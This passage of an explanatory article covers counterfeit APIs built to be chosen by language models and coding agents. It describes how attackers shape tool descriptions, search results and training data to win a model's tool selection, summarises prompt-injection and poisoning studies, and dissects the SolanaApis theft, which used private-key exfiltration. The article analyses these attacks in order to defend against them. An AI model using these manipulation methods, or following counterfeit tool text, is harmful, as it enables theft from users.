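# "API SEO": counterfeit APIs aimed at the language models that choose which API to call

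## How a language model comes to call an API

An API (application programming interface) lets one program use another, often a company's server, to do things like send an email, charge a card or look up the weather. Programmers used to choose these services themselves. Large language models, the systems behind ChatGPT and Claude, now make more and more of these choices, especially as coding agents, which write, install and run code with little step-by-step direction. "API SEO" is an informal label for promoting an API so that language models select it, by analogy with the search engine optimisation (SEO) that websites use to rank higher in Google's results. The malicious version uses a counterfeit API, which an attacker runs while passing it off as a vendor's own or as a legitimate service for the vendor's platform.

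Little has been written under the label "API SEO". BrandStory's *API SEO*, a marketing agency's guide, uses the term for the legitimate practice of making a vendor's documentation easy for developers to find. Osmani's *Agentic Engine Optimization (AEO)* uses the term in its title for making documentation suit coding agents, which is also legitimate. Security researchers mostly describe the counterfeit-API attack by its mechanism, and it is unclear who first called it "API SEO".

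### One email, from the user's sentence to the network

Suppose a shop owner types "email the customer that order 12345 has shipped" into an assistant, and the shop sends its mail through Postmark, a company that delivers email for other firms' software. The model cannot send anything. It only produces text, and a program around it, the client, has to turn that text into a request over the network. Going by Postmark's *Sending email with API*, the request looks roughly like this:

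```
POST /email          (host: api.postmarkapp.com)
X-Postmark-Server-Token: [the shop's secret token]

{ "From": "shop@example.com",
  "To": "customer@example.com",
  "Subject": "Order 12345",
  "TextBody": "Your parcel left us this morning." }
```

The host and path on the top line make up the endpoint, the web address to which a program sends an API request. The token underneath is an API key, a secret string that ties the request to the shop's account. The message follows in JSON, a plain-text format for structured data. If the request succeeds, Postmark's server returns a short reply with an error code of 0, the word "OK" and an identifier for the message. If the token is wrong or missing, the server refuses the request.

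Few programmers write such requests by hand. Instead, they install a package of ready-made code from a public catalogue called a registry. Postmark offers a JavaScript package through npm, that language's main registry. The package supplies the address and the header, so a program needs only a line or two to send a message. Tessl's catalogue for coding agents includes sample code for this task, which reads the token from an environment variable, a setting stored on the machine rather than in the source code. The running program still sends the token to whatever address the code contains.

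An assistant can also reach Postmark through an MCP server, a program that offers tools to a model through the Model Context Protocol, an open standard. The client requests the server's list of tools, which gives the name, description and input specification of each, and passes the list to the model. The model outputs a tool's name and the input values, the client forwards them to the MCP server, and the server makes the request to Postmark. The result goes back to the model, which reports to the user.

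PortSwigger's *Web LLM attacks*, a security tutorial, describes much the same loop and warns that users may not know that an API call took place. The protocol's documentation recommends but does not require that a person be able to refuse a call and that clients show the inputs before sending them.

A coding agent writes the API request into a program that keeps running long after the conversation ends. If it picks a bad API address for a shop's email, every email the shop sends goes there until somebody reads the code, whereas an assistant that makes the same mistake while sending one email misdirects only that email.

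### Three routes: memory, search and catalogue

The shop owner's sentence contains no web address. The model recalls one from its training, finds one through web search or documentation, or picks a tool that somebody has installed or catalogued. An attacker has to influence something different in each case.

**Memory.** A model trained on Postmark's documentation, and on many programs that use it, can write the endpoint and header name without looking anything up. Evil Martians' *3 rules for getting AI agents to find, use—and not exploit—your devtool*, a consultancy's guide for companies that sell developer tools, traces this "baked-in" knowledge to big public datasets such as The Pile and C4. An attacker therefore has to get text into such datasets before training starts, such as documentation, sample code or forum answers that pair a common task with the attacker's address. PortSwigger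 classes this as training data poisoning and attributes it to training data that is too broad or comes from untrusted sources. The method is slow because planted text has no effect until a company trains a model on it. It is also hard to undo, because taking the page down does not change a model already trained on it.

How much planted text this would take is an open question. Hackaday's *It Only Takes A Handful Of Samples To Poison Any Size LLM* (2025) describes an experiment by Anthropic, the company that makes Claude, in which a relatively small number of poisoned documents made models produce gibberish in response to the word "sudo", a common Linux command. The models ranged from 600 million to 13 billion parameters (the adjustable numbers that training sets). But gibberish is a much cruder effect than a plausible wrong address. Hackaday's writer wondered whether lies would be as easy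 to plant, which the experiment did not test.

A model working from memory can also produce an address that never existed, and an attacker may then register it. Unit 42, the threat research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, reports that this is already happening.

**Search.** An agent with web access can read the documentation first, but finding it can be difficult. Anon's *Designing APIs that agents can discover* (2026), a company blog post, describes a typical attempt. The agent searches for the vendor's documentation, lands on the marketing site and goes from there to the documentation page. That page appears empty because its text loads only after a browser runs the page's scripts. The agent then tries likely paths such as /api and /developers, some of which lead nowhere. When it finds something that resembles documentation, it guesses the endpoint, parameter names and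 authentication method. Its first call fails, so it changes the call and tries again.

An attacker therefore needs to publish a page that the search returns and that fits the request better than the vendor's own page. This can be easy, because a plain page with a complete example spares the agent the guesswork, especially when the vendor's documentation is unreadable to machines. Tricks from ordinary search optimisation may also help the page rank higher. Schneier on Security's *The Rise of Large-Language-Model Optimization* describes an early example, in which scammers hid misleading keywords in pages to fool search engines. Unlike planted training text, such a page can work on the day it goes up, and against any model whose search finds it, but it stops working for new searches once the host or the search engine removes it.

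*Prompt Injection Attack to Tool Selection in LLM Agents* (Shi, Yuan and colleagues, 2025) divides a language model's choice from a library of tools into two steps. Each tool has a document with its name, description and technical details. First, a retriever, which is a separate and simpler program, converts the user's request and every tool document into vectors (lists of numbers that represent meaning) and selects the *k* documents most similar to the request. The language model then receives the request and the names and descriptions of those *k* tools, and outputs the name of one.

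The attacker's tool has to get through both steps:

P(tool runs) = P(tool is on the shortlist) × P(model picks it, given that it is on the shortlist)

If a model chose an attacker's API 80% of the time when it saw the description, but the description reached the shortlist for only half of the relevant requests, the attacker would get 40% of those requests. The description therefore has to match the way users phrase the task and also beat the rival descriptions on the shortlist. When only a few tools are installed, there may be no retriever, and the difficulty is instead that a person or an agent must first install the attacker's server.

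The model is vulnerable because it judges a tool by text that the tool's publisher wrote. In *Make an API AI-Ready*, part of the documentation for its API software, WSO2 advises publishers that the description is the main signal an agent uses to decide whether an API is relevant, and a dishonest publisher can act on the same advice. Names offer little protection, since the Model Context Protocol (MCP) requires no central check on them. Two servers may both offer a tool called "search", and even a server's own name need not be unique. The protocol's documentation tells clients to treat a tool's annotations, which are notes on how it behaves, as untrusted unless the server is trusted. Shi and colleagues add that an MCP server can change a tool's description after the agent has approved the tool, so checking it once at installation is not enough.

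A single task often combines these routes. A coding agent might recall that Postmark sends email, search for the current request format, and install a package from npm. Even if it recalls the vendor correctly, the search result or the package can still introduce a counterfeit.

### Two forms of counterfeit

An attacker may copy a vendor's name or the look of its interface so that the model, or the developer who accepts its suggestion, mistakes the counterfeit API for the real one. Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams* describes SolanaApis as a fake API that imitated an interface to the Solana blockchain and sent developers' transactions to the attacker's wallet.

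A counterfeit API may offer something the vendor does not provide. *Scam2Prompt* (2025), a study of scam addresses in the output of language models, examines a case involving pump.fun, a site for trading crypto tokens on Solana. The official site had no API for the specific function requested. The attacker's documentation covered that function, so it looked like a perfect match, and the model was led to it because the request was so specific. Legitimate third-party services for pump.fun did exist, but using them took more engineering work than a single API call.

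This difference affects how a counterfeit can be detected. An impostor can be compared with the original: Postmark publishes its endpoint, so a request for "Postmark" that goes to an unrelated host is suspicious. A service that fills a gap has no original, and the vendor's documentation doesn't cover it, so one has to look at what the service asks for. In the pump.fun case, that was enough to identify the counterfeit, because the malicious API demanded the user's private key, the secret that controls a crypto wallet, in the request. *Scam2Prompt* explains that a legitimate service never needs this key. The user signs each transaction on their own machine and sends only the signature, which others can verify with a matching public key.

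Resembling another API does not by itself make an API counterfeit. Akamai, a network and security company, notes that many providers, including OpenRouter and Hugging Face, emulate the request format OpenAI introduced for its chat models. They do it openly, so customers can switch without rewriting their programs. An independent service built around another company's platform is not a counterfeit either, as long as it is honest about who runs it and what it does with the data.

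Three better-known attacks overlap with this one. Typosquatting is registering a likely misspelling of a real name in the hope that somebody types it by mistake. Slopsquatting, as Trend Micro defines it, is registering package names that models have invented and putting malware in the packages. Prompt injection is text in outside content that a model treats as an instruction, whereas a counterfeit API may need only documentation that seems to answer the request. The line between these two is blurry, though, since Shi and colleagues class their manipulated tool descriptions as prompt injection.

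### What the attacker gains

If the email request above goes to a counterfeit endpoint, the attacker receives the token. Postmark accepts mail only from sender addresses that the account holder has confirmed, so a thief with the token can send email from the shop's real address. The shop can replace a stolen token. A stolen private key is worse, because whoever holds it can empty the wallet, and no vendor can reverse the transfer.

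The attacker also gets all the data the program sends, including the customer's address and the text of the message. Ordinary web encryption does not prevent this, because it protects the request only on its way to the server, and the attacker owns the server. Liu, Shou and colleagues (2026), in *Your Agent Is Mine*, studied operators in a similar position, the third-party routers that pass agents' requests on to several model providers. These routers see every request and reply in plain text, and no provider uses cryptography to guarantee that a message arrives unaltered. Liu and colleagues distinguish two main attacks, stealing secrets and inserting content into the traffic. A counterfeit API that forwards requests to the real vendor could do both while everything appeared to work.

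Whoever controls an API can also change the answer the model gives. Zhao, Khazanchi and colleagues (2024), in *Attacks on Third-Party APIs of Large Language Models*, altered the replies from weather, encyclopedia and news APIs before GPT-3.5-turbo and an early Gemini model used them to answer questions. Swapping the names of people, organisations and places in news replies succeeded in 84% of cases with GPT-3.5-turbo and 70% with Gemini. Adding false names while leaving the true ones in place succeeded in only 12% and 8%, respectively. Both models are long out of date, so the rates are mainly of historical interest, but Zhao and colleagues' explanation for the failures is still useful. They say the attacks tended to fail when the false data contradicted what the models had learned in training or was absurd, such as a midlife crisis starting at the age of one.

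A program usually calls an API for something the model does not know, so the model has little to check the reply against. In the email example, the reply is the only evidence that the message went out, and a counterfeit API can return an error code of 0 and the word "OK" without sending anything.

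## Which vendors coding agents choose when none is named

The shop in the email example already used Postmark, but a developer without an email provider may just tell a coding agent to add email and let it choose one. In *What Claude Code Actually Chooses*, Ong and Vikati (2026) gave requests like this to Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, without naming any product. Of the 102 email answers with a clear choice, 64 chose Resend, a competitor of Postmark. Amplifying, the company behind the study, reports that none chose Postmark.

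An attacker can learn from these habits which vendors are worth imitating. A counterfeit Resend would match far more of Claude Code's choices than a counterfeit Postmark. The attacker can also see where no vendor dominates yet. A fake service that claims to fill a gap would probably face the least competition there.

### Early measurements of provider bias

Provider bias is a model's tendency to write code for some companies' services and neglect comparable ones. In *The Invisible Hand* (January 2025), Zhang, Zhai and colleagues made the first large attempt to measure it. One of them had asked Gemini 1.5 Flash, a Google model, to debug a program that used Dragonfly, an open-source speech recognition package. The model rewrote the program to use Google Speech Recognition, a paid service.

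The team collected 30 scenarios in which a program needs an outside service, such as speech recognition or cloud hosting, and found at least five services from different providers for each. They turned these into 17,014 prompts for seven models, including GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet. Some prompts asked for new code. Others supplied code that already used a service and asked the model to debug, extend, test or tidy it, or translate it into Java. The team used software to identify the providers in the answers from library names and web addresses.

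For new code, Zhang and colleagues used the Gini index, a standard measure of inequality. If *n* providers appear in a scenario, and *x*ᵢ is the number of times a model uses provider *i*, counting from the least used to the most used, then

GI = Σ (2*i* − *n* − 1) *x*ᵢ / (*n* Σ *x*ᵢ)

An index of 0 means the model uses all providers equally, and an index near 1 means one provider gets almost all the uses. If one of ten providers gets 91 uses and the other nine get one each, the index is 0.81. The median in the study was 0.80, so the typical scenario was about that lopsided.

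Google was the most common choice in 27% to 43% of scenarios, depending on the model, partly because it has a service for 28 of the 30 scenarios, while Amazon has one for 20 and Microsoft for 18. In the 15 scenarios where all three compete, most models preferred Amazon. The models rarely chose Microsoft. Its Azure platform has 23% of the cloud market, according to a report cited by Zhang and colleagues, but only 2% of the models' cloud-hosting code used Azure, so the bias does not simply mirror market share.

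When the prompt included existing code, the models replaced the user's service with another provider's in 11,582 of 571,057 answers, or about 2%. Claude 3.5 Sonnet had the highest rate, at 3.9%. Most replacements happened during translation and debugging, and very few happened when the user asked for tests or new features. In a separate test, 87% of human participants accepted the code without noticing the change. An explicit instruction to keep the named service cut GPT-4o's replacement rate from 26.9% to 7.5% on a set of prompts that included many known to trigger replacements.

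All seven models are now well out of date, and they answered single prompts rather than working as agents. The prompt for new code also specified "open-source services", which may have made the models less likely to choose some commercial vendors.

### Models that favour their own maker's services

When Google's model switches a user to a Google service, the cause may be self-preference or just how common Google's services are. *Do LLMs Favor Their Providers?* (Catal, Wolf and colleagues, 2026) separated the two with a benchmark of 20 tasks that several large vendors can perform. The study tested ten models with ties to Google, Amazon, IBM, Alibaba or the Microsoft–OpenAI partnership. Its controls were three models from DeepSeek, Mistral and xAI, which don't sell these services.

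The study measures bias as how much more often a model uses its own developer's services than the control models do. If a Google model used Google's services in 60% of its code and the control models did so in 40% of theirs, the bias would be 20 percentage points. Six of the ten models showed a statistically significant bias when writing single pieces of code. The largest was 18.8 points, for Gemini 2.5 Flash.

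The bias grew when the models worked as agents and built a ten-file project. It reached 39.2 points for Gemini 2.5 Flash, and rose from 12.2 to 30.8 for Amazon's Nova Pro and from 7.9 to 18.2 for OpenAI's GPT-5.4 Mini. The models also tended to keep using the vendor they chose first. When Gemini 2.5 Flash used Google in the first file, it used Google in 90.3% of the later files, even though those files were for separate tasks. An attacker would gain little from this with a single fake endpoint, but might gain more by imitating a whole platform.

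Catal and colleagues measured the code but didn't investigate its causes, and they warn against reading the results as evidence of intent. They didn't test any Anthropic models for self-preference.

### What Claude Code and its rivals install

Ong and Vikati's study is closer to everyday use, because the agent, Claude Code, works inside a project and can install what it picks. They wrote 100 prompts, such as "i need a database, what should i use", with five phrasings for each of 20 categories. For each of four small projects, they ran the prompts that suited it three times on each of three Claude models, which gave 2,430 responses. Of these, 2,073 had a clear first choice. In more than half of the rest, Claude Code asked a question or requested permission before going further.

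Claude Code's most common choice was to write the feature itself, which it did in 252 cases, or 12%. In some categories, it picked the same product nearly every time. It chose Stripe for 64 of 70 payment picks, and the other six were custom mock-ups, so it never picked a rival payment company. It chose GitHub Actions, a service that tests and deploys code automatically, for 152 of 162 picks in that category. Rephrasing a question changed the top pick about a quarter of the time, mostly in categories without a clear leader.

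Claude Code itself read the responses and extracted the picks, which could introduce errors that favour some answers. Ong and Vikati acknowledge that they cannot tell whether a product is picked because it is better or because it appears more often in the training data. Amplifying also has a commercial interest, because it sells tool vendors help with measuring and improving how coding agents find and use their products (Amplifying, 2026).

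In July, Ong and Vikati repeated the test with Fable 5, a newer Claude model (*What Fable Actually Chooses*, 2026). The table gives the top choice in each of six categories and its share of the picks.

| Category | February 2026, three Claude models | July 2026, Fable 5 |
|---|---|---|
| Payments | Stripe, 91% | Stripe, 100% |
| Automated testing and deployment | GitHub Actions, 94% | GitHub Actions, 100% |
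| Email | Resend, 63% | Resend, 52% |
| Databases | PostgreSQL, 58% | PostgreSQL, 53% |
| Caching (keeping data ready for reuse) | Redis, 42% | Custom code, 57% |
| Feature flags (switches for parts of a program) | Custom code, 69% | Custom code, 71% |

Custom code made up 21.4% of Fable 5's picks, compared with 11% for Sonnet 4.5, the most conventional of the February models. This gives counterfeit APIs fewer chances to be chosen, since a feature that the model writes itself may not call an outside service. But in about a third of the custom solutions, the agent named a vendor as a later replacement.

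Other agents choose differently. *What Codex Actually Chooses (vs Claude Code)* (Amplifying, 2026) compares Claude Code with OpenAI's Codex on 1,452 picks in 12 categories. This time, Amplifying reviewed the responses by hand. The two agents had the same top choice in seven categories. In six of those it was custom code, and in the seventh it was Grafana, for collecting logs.

The largest company-linked differences involved products that the agents' makers had bought. Codex picked Statsig, which OpenAI owns, in 27% of its feature-flag answers, and Claude Code never picked it. Claude Code picked Bun, which Anthropic bought in December 2025, in 63% of its answers about JavaScript runtimes, compared with 13% for Codex. Both results fit the self-preference Catal and colleagues found, although the Bun figures come from only 30 answers per agent. Amplifying calls the differences correlational because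 more documentation or different training data could also explain them. More recently, Amplifying (2026) reported that Dots, an OpenAI agent, defaults to OpenAI's platform when it builds apps. Amplifying also found that asking the same questions in English and Chinese led to different choices.

Armature, which also sells services to tool vendors, ran a larger study. Pinggy's *What AI Coding Agents Pick When You Let Them Choose Your Stack* (2026), a company blog post, summarises Armature's 5,292 published sessions with Claude Code, Codex and Cursor. Given the same task, all three agents picked the same vendor only 42% of the time. An attacker who studied one agent's choices would therefore often guess wrong about the others, except in a category like payments, where the agents chose Stripe nine times out of ten.

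The sessions also show that asking a model for its opinion is a poor way to predict what it will use in its code. The agents mentioned PayPal in 139 sessions and never picked it. *A Study of LLMs' Preferences for Libraries and Programming Languages* (Twist, Harman and colleagues, 2025) found much the same with eight older models, whose recommendations only weakly predicted what they used in code.

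### Why Resend and not Postmark

Fable 5 listed Postmark as an alternative in 48% of its email answers but never picked it, so something other than unfamiliarity with Postmark must lead Claude to choose Resend.

Claude sometimes gives a reason for its choice. API Evangelist's blog post *Artificial Intelligence Choosing My Tools and Services* (2026) describes building a signup form with Claude. Claude proposed Resend, citing the "simplest API, free tier, just an API key", and offered Postmark, Mailgun or Amazon's email service as alternatives. The reason is plausible, but a model can produce a plausible reason for a choice it would have made anyway.

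Claude Code probably chooses largely from what it learned in training, since it searched the web in only about 30% of Armature's sessions. Fame alone doesn't explain the result, because SendGrid, another email provider, came up in more than half of Fable 5's email answers but was never chosen. Newer models also seem to choose newer products more often. In Amplifying's February study, Sonnet 4.5 picked the database tool Prisma, from 2019, in 79% of cases in one JavaScript project, whereas Opus 4.6 always picked Drizzle, from 2022. In the Python project, Resend's share of email picks rose from 21% with Sonnet 4.5 to 50% with Opus 4.6. Twist and colleagues tested older models and found the opposite tendency, with well-established libraries chosen over fast-growing ones.

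The choice also depends on the project. Fable 5 picked Resend in 86% of email answers for a project built with Next.js, a web framework, but in the Python project it mostly wrote its own code using SMTP, the standard protocol for sending mail. Ong and Vikati point out that Vercel, the host Fable 5 always picked for the Next.js project, cannot hold an SMTP connection open. Fable 5's frequent choice of Resend is therefore partly a sensible response to the hosting.

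Price terms and documentation seem to matter more when an agent looks things up. In Armature's study, which included two agents that search more than Claude Code does, agents chose Resend in 35.6% of email picks and Postmark in 27.4%. Agents regularly chose Postmark over Mailgun after reading "1-day retention" in the description of Mailgun's free plan. Codex searched the web in 94% of sessions, so a line on a pricing page has many more chances to influence it than Claude Code.

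Neither Armature nor Amplifying varied one factor at a time, so the relative weight of memory, documentation and price is still unclear. In *How AI Coding Agents Choose Your Stack*, Ong attributes the choices to a mix of training data, project constraints, vendor influence and user settings. He largely rules out the system prompt, the standing instructions a company gives its model, because the extracted prompts for Claude Code and Codex are mostly neutral about vendors.

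Signing up is another obstacle. Fable 5 once wrote its own login system instead of using Supabase, a database and login service. Its stated reason was that Supabase needed an account and keys that only a person could create. Because the owner of a counterfeit API makes money from theft rather than subscriptions, the API can be free, simple to call and usable without an account.

### Writing documentation for agents

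Honest vendors try to influence these choices too, partly through agentic engine optimization. Osmani recommends llms.txt, a plain text file at the root of a website that lists and describes the documentation pages, so that an agent can go straight to the right one. Another file, skill.md, sets out what a product can do, the inputs it needs and its limits. He also advises short pages, because most agents can handle only 100,000 to 200,000 tokens (short pieces of text, often parts of words) at once, and a single Cisco guide takes up 193,217.

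Some vendors go further and put their product inside the agent. Resend's *Send emails with Claude Code* offers an official plugin that installs the company's MCP server and a set of email instructions with one command. Ong and Vikati, in *Claude Code's Leak*, searched the agent's leaked source code and found built-in references to more than 120 companies. Claude Code can fetch documentation for some of them without a link from the user.

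All this is lawful when a vendor describes its own product honestly and under its own name, but an llms.txt file contains no proof of who wrote it.

There is little evidence that the lawful version changes what agents choose. Osmani, who works at Google Cloud, doesn't test this and discloses that Google Search does not officially recommend llms.txt. Evil Martians report that AI companies' crawlers don't request the file unprompted, so it mainly helps when a person pastes a link or an agent follows one. Stripe uses its file to steer agents away from outdated versions of its API, which is about correct use rather than promotion.

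Evil Martians also asked Claude, ChatGPT and Gemini more than 50 developer questions and recorded the pages they retrieved. Vendors' comparison pages were the most common source for Claude and Gemini, while ChatGPT drew most often on Reddit. Products with specific claims, such as a response time or a fixed monthly price, tended to win over products with vague ones. The consultancy sells this kind of work. It also observed existing pages rather than rewriting them, so the winning products may have won because they were better.

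Catal and colleagues come closer to a controlled test, because in some runs they put documentation for several competing vendors in the prompt. When the models worked as agents, the documentation cut Nova Pro's bias towards Amazon from 51.0 to 10.6 points and GPT-5.4 Mini's bias from 22.8 to 13.5. But Gemini 2.5 Pro's bias towards Google rose from 13.1 to 19.6. The experiment did not test whether a vendor gains by rewriting its own documentation. The effect of wording is clearer in attack research, where malicious tool descriptions and manipulated plugins have shifted models' choices.

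Amplifying now sells vendors an experiment in which they change their documentation, rerun the same task and compare the results. An attacker with access to the same agent could do this too.

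## SolanaApis, a counterfeit API that ChatGPT recommended

In November 2024, a man lost about $2,500 after running a trading script in which ChatGPT had put the address of SolanaApis, a counterfeit API for the token-trading site pump.fun. The API was counterfeit in both senses, because its name suggested an official Solana interface and it offered a function that pump.fun did not provide. The victim published the whole conversation, but accounts differ on how ChatGPT got the address.

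### From a trading script to an empty wallet

According to *I never expected that AI stole my wallet* (Azuma, 2024), the victim, a crypto trader who posts on X as r_ocky.eth, wanted a pump.fun trading bot. The published conversation is about buying a token, although some reports instead describe a "bump bot" for advertising on Discord.

He gave ChatGPT a token's address and asked for a Python script to buy the token. The first draft was for Ethereum, so he replied that the script had to work on Solana, a different blockchain. ChatGPT then wrote a more general script using spl-token, a legitimate library for handling Solana tokens. Both drafts were harmless, though the second left him to fill in the trading platform and token address, and *Scam2Prompt* notes that it had a fundamental flaw.

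Then he told ChatGPT that the script had to buy the token from pump.fun. The next draft sent a web request to api[.]solanaapis[.]com, with a path ending in /pumpfun/buy. The request had a field for the wallet's private key, and a comment beside it told him to replace the placeholder with his actual key. According to heise online's *ChatGPT*, a news report on the theft, another comment labelled this block of data as the payload of the request. Anyone who read the code and knew what a private key was could have seen the problem.

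The script first failed with a TypeError, which Python raises when a program uses a value of the wrong type. He pasted the error into the chat and ChatGPT explained it, but the next attempt also failed with a TypeError. After several rounds of this, he got a version that ran, and it sent his key to the attacker. Within 30 minutes, everything in his main wallet was gone. He later wrote that "it's easy to make mistakes" when in a hurry.

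*Scam2Prompt* cites the debugging as evidence that real users will run code containing unknown addresses even after many chances to review it. One victim is too few to show how common this is, but he was probably not unusual, since most participants in Zhang and colleagues' test of swapped providers did not notice the swap.

He asked ChatGPT where to complain and sent the conversation to OpenAI. He also reported a fraudulent repository to the code-sharing site GitHub, which quickly removed it, according to heise online. OpenAI had not replied when Azuma wrote about the case the next day.

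The victim also traced the money through Solana's public records to an address he suspected was the attacker's main wallet. Azuma reports that it had collected more than $100,000, while BornCity's *ChatGPT* (2024), a blog post from two days later, puts the total at $75,000. These totals don't show how many people lost money or how many of them had used a chatbot. The $2,500 is the only loss in these reports that clearly followed from ChatGPT's recommendation.

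### Why the counterfeit matched the request

No official documentation competed with the attacker's, which was worded much like the victim's request. Both mentioned Solana, pump.fun and buying a token, according to an appendix to *Scam2Prompt*.

Each correction the victim made increased the chance that ChatGPT would recommend the counterfeit. Many legitimate services and libraries could help a program buy a crypto token, but fewer work on Solana, and fewer still on pump.fun. Specific requests usually get better code from a language model, but here they ruled out most of the legitimate alternatives.

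The counterfeit also needed less code, because SolanaApis promised to build, sign and send a transaction in one request. bloXroute's *Create Swap Transaction*, the documentation for a legitimate pump.fun service, describes an endpoint that takes the user's wallet address and returns an unsigned transaction. The user's program still has to sign it and send it to the Solana network.

It is unclear how much this simplicity mattered. *Scam2Prompt* bases its explanation on the similarity between the two texts. To test that explanation, someone would have to change the documentation and see whether ChatGPT still chose the counterfeit.

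The gap may be narrower today, because pump.fun now publishes official developer documentation on GitHub, along with skills, which are instruction files for AI agents. This does not mean that pump.fun runs a trading API. Impostors are also still active. OSV's *MAL-2026-10034* (2026), an entry in a public vulnerability database, describes a package from July 2026 that posed as a pump.fun toolkit and stole credentials.

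### Sending a private key and signing locally

A wallet's private key authorises payments by producing signatures, and its public key, which is safe to share, lets others check them. If *k* is the private key, *K* the public key and *m* a transaction, the owner's software computes a signature *s*, and the network checks it:

*s* = Sign(*k*, *m*)

Verify(*K*, *m*, *s*) = true or false

The network carries out the transaction only if the check succeeds. The signature is valid only for that transaction, so changing the amount or the recipient makes the check fail. Nobody can feasibly derive the private key from the signature. If the victim had wanted to buy $50 worth of a token, a signature on that purchase would have authorised only that purchase. His private key let the attacker sign any transaction, including one that took the full $2,500.

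In outline, the two designs look like this:

```
Key disclosure
  send (private key, order) to the service
  the service signs and submits whatever it likes

Local signing
  send (public key, order) to the service
  receive an unsigned transaction
  sign it with the private key on the user's own machine
  send the signed transaction to the Solana network
```

PumpPortal, an unofficial API for pump.fun, lets a user's program sign transactions locally. The program sends its public key, the token, the amount, whether to buy or sell, and how far the price may move before the trade fails. PumpPortal returns a transaction, which the program signs and submits through a server the user chooses.

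PumpPortal's sample code has a placeholder for the private key, as ChatGPT's script did, so telling the two designs apart requires tracing where the key goes. PumpPortal's code passes it to a signing function on the user's machine, while ChatGPT's script put it in a web request.

A request for an existing wallet's private key is a strong warning sign, because all the operator gains from the key is the ability to sign without the user.

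Some honest services sign for their customers. Solana Compass' *PumpPortal*, a guide to the service as of October 2026, describes a second option called Lightning, in which PumpPortal signs and submits each trade from a wallet linked to the customer's API key. Like SolanaApis, Lightning takes only one request per trade. But the customer creates a new wallet for these trades and moves some money into it, rather than handing over the key to a wallet they already use. PumpPortal launched in 2024, but it is unclear whether Lightning was available in November 2024.

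A program that signs transactions locally also has to check what each one does before signing it. Socket's *pumpfun* (2026), a security company's audit of an add-on for coding agents, warns that the add-on signs whatever transaction the remote service returns, without inspecting it. An attacker who took over the service could return a transaction that transfers the user's funds or gives the attacker control over them. A counterfeit API could do the same from the start, without ever asking for the private key, the request that gave SolanaApis away.

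| Design | What the program sends | Who signs | What a dishonest operator could take |
|---|---|---|---|
| SolanaApis | The private key of the user's wallet | The operator | Everything in the wallet |
| PumpPortal, local signing | A public key and an order | The user's program | Whatever the program signs without checking |
| PumpPortal, Lightning | An API key and an order | The operator | Everything in the separate trading wallet |

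A separate wallet would have limited the damage in all three cases. heise online advises developers to use a test account instead of a live one. That is not always possible. PumpPortal, for example, has no test network, but according to Solana Compass it recommends testing with small amounts. If the victim had done this, he would have lost only that amount.

### How the attackers promoted SolanaApis

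The campaign was new when it caught its best-known victim. CryptoSlate's *Blockchain security firm warns of AI code poisoning risk* cites Yu Xian, founder of the blockchain security firm SlowMist, as saying that the domain was two months old and the website consisted only of documents and code repositories. Scam Sniffer, another security firm, said that a GitHub user called "solanaapisdev" had created multiple repositories in recent months.

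The attackers also spread their documentation beyond GitHub. *Scam2Prompt*, drawing on a security researcher's investigation posted on X, lists the API publishing and testing platform Postman, the question-and-answer network Stack Exchange, and the blogging platform Medium. All three already had a reputation with developers and search engines. Somebody who looked up SolanaApis could find the same address in several places that seemed independent.

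In July 2025, Netcraft, a company that detects and takes down online scams, described a larger operation with blog tutorials, forum answers and dozens of GitHub repositories. Several fake GitHub accounts shared a project called Moonshot-Volume-Bot, which had the counterfeit API built in. The accounts had detailed biographies, profile pictures, linked social media accounts and credible coding activity.

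Someone who copies a ready-made bot gets the API's address along with the rest of the code, and may never notice that the program uses an outside service. A coding agent that borrows code from the repository could make the same mistake. People reading documentation, by contrast, are already looking for an API and may compare a few.

Netcraft found at least five people who had copied the malicious code into their own public projects. There could be more, since a search of public projects misses private ones. Some of the five projects showed signs of AI coding tools, including Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent. This doesn't establish that an AI tool suggested the API, since a developer could have copied the bot by hand and then used Cursor to adapt it. Netcraft doesn't say how much money, if any, the five people lost.

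The campaign continued after GitHub removed one repository in November 2024. Netcraft found the API on a second address, api[.]primeapis[.]com. By August 2025 the main site had moved from solanaapis[.]com to solanaapis[.]net, where *Scam2Prompt* found it still running.

An attacker who relies on search can change domains easily, because updated documentation can send new visitors to the new address as soon as a search engine finds it. If the attacker relied on a model's memory instead, they would have to keep the old domain running as well.

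### Did ChatGPT remember the address or find it?

Yu Xian called the theft a case of AI poisoning. Azuma took this to mean that scam material had probably entered ChatGPT's training data and the model had later reproduced it. Scam Sniffer also said that scammers were polluting training data with harmful crypto code, and heise online gave much the same explanation.

CryptoSlate reported Yu Xian's warning but added an editor's note that disagreed with it. The victim's screenshot shows a "sources" section, so ChatGPT appears to have searched the web. The editor argued that, if so, ChatGPT had failed to recognise a scam link among its search results, which is not poisoning.

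The dates strongly support the editor. OpenAI's *Introducing ChatGPT search* (2024) announced the search feature on 31 October, three weeks before the theft. ChatGPT could run a search even if the victim had not asked for one. Answers that used search included links and a "Sources" button.

The search feature ran on a version of GPT-4o, and *Scam2Prompt* gives October 2023 as the end of that model's training data. If Yu Xian was right about the domain's age, the attackers registered it around September 2024, almost a year later, so the training data could not have contained the address. Pump.fun only took off in 2024, so GPT-4o would have had little information about it without a search.

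The October 2023 date comes from OpenAI's developer documentation, and ChatGPT may have been running a later version. Even if it was, the attackers' pages would have had to get from the web into a finished model within about two months, which is very unlikely. At launch, search was open only to paying subscribers and people on a waiting list. It is unclear whether the victim was one of them, though the "sources" section suggests that he was.

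The screenshot doesn't show which page led ChatGPT to the counterfeit. It could have been the attackers' own documentation, a GitHub repository or a post on Medium. Removing one repository would do little to prevent a repeat if the search engine was returning the documentation site.

Some of the disagreement is about the word "poisoning". The attackers planted misleading pages, probably on purpose. CryptoSlate describes the poisoning as apparently deliberate but attributes ChatGPT's recommendation to search. The evidence does not support the narrower claim that those pages had entered ChatGPT's training data by November 2024.

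*Scam2Prompt* makes that narrower claim. It presents the theft as an example of the danger from malicious training data, although its study excludes anything a model finds through a search engine. If ChatGPT found the address by searching, the paper's opening example falls outside the study's scope. The main results don't depend on the example, because they come from models that wrote scam addresses into code without searching.

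The two explanations call for different remedies. OpenAI could have blocked the site in its search results once somebody reported it, but that would not have removed an address learned in training. According to Azuma, Yu Xian suggested adding some form of code review to ChatGPT. That could work in both cases because it would check the finished code.

SolanaApis may have entered training data since then. The training data for Gemini 2.5 Pro runs to January 2025 and for Claude Sonnet 4 to March 2025. The campaign had been online for months by both dates, but it is unknown whether either model learned the address.

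### Were the attackers aiming at language models?

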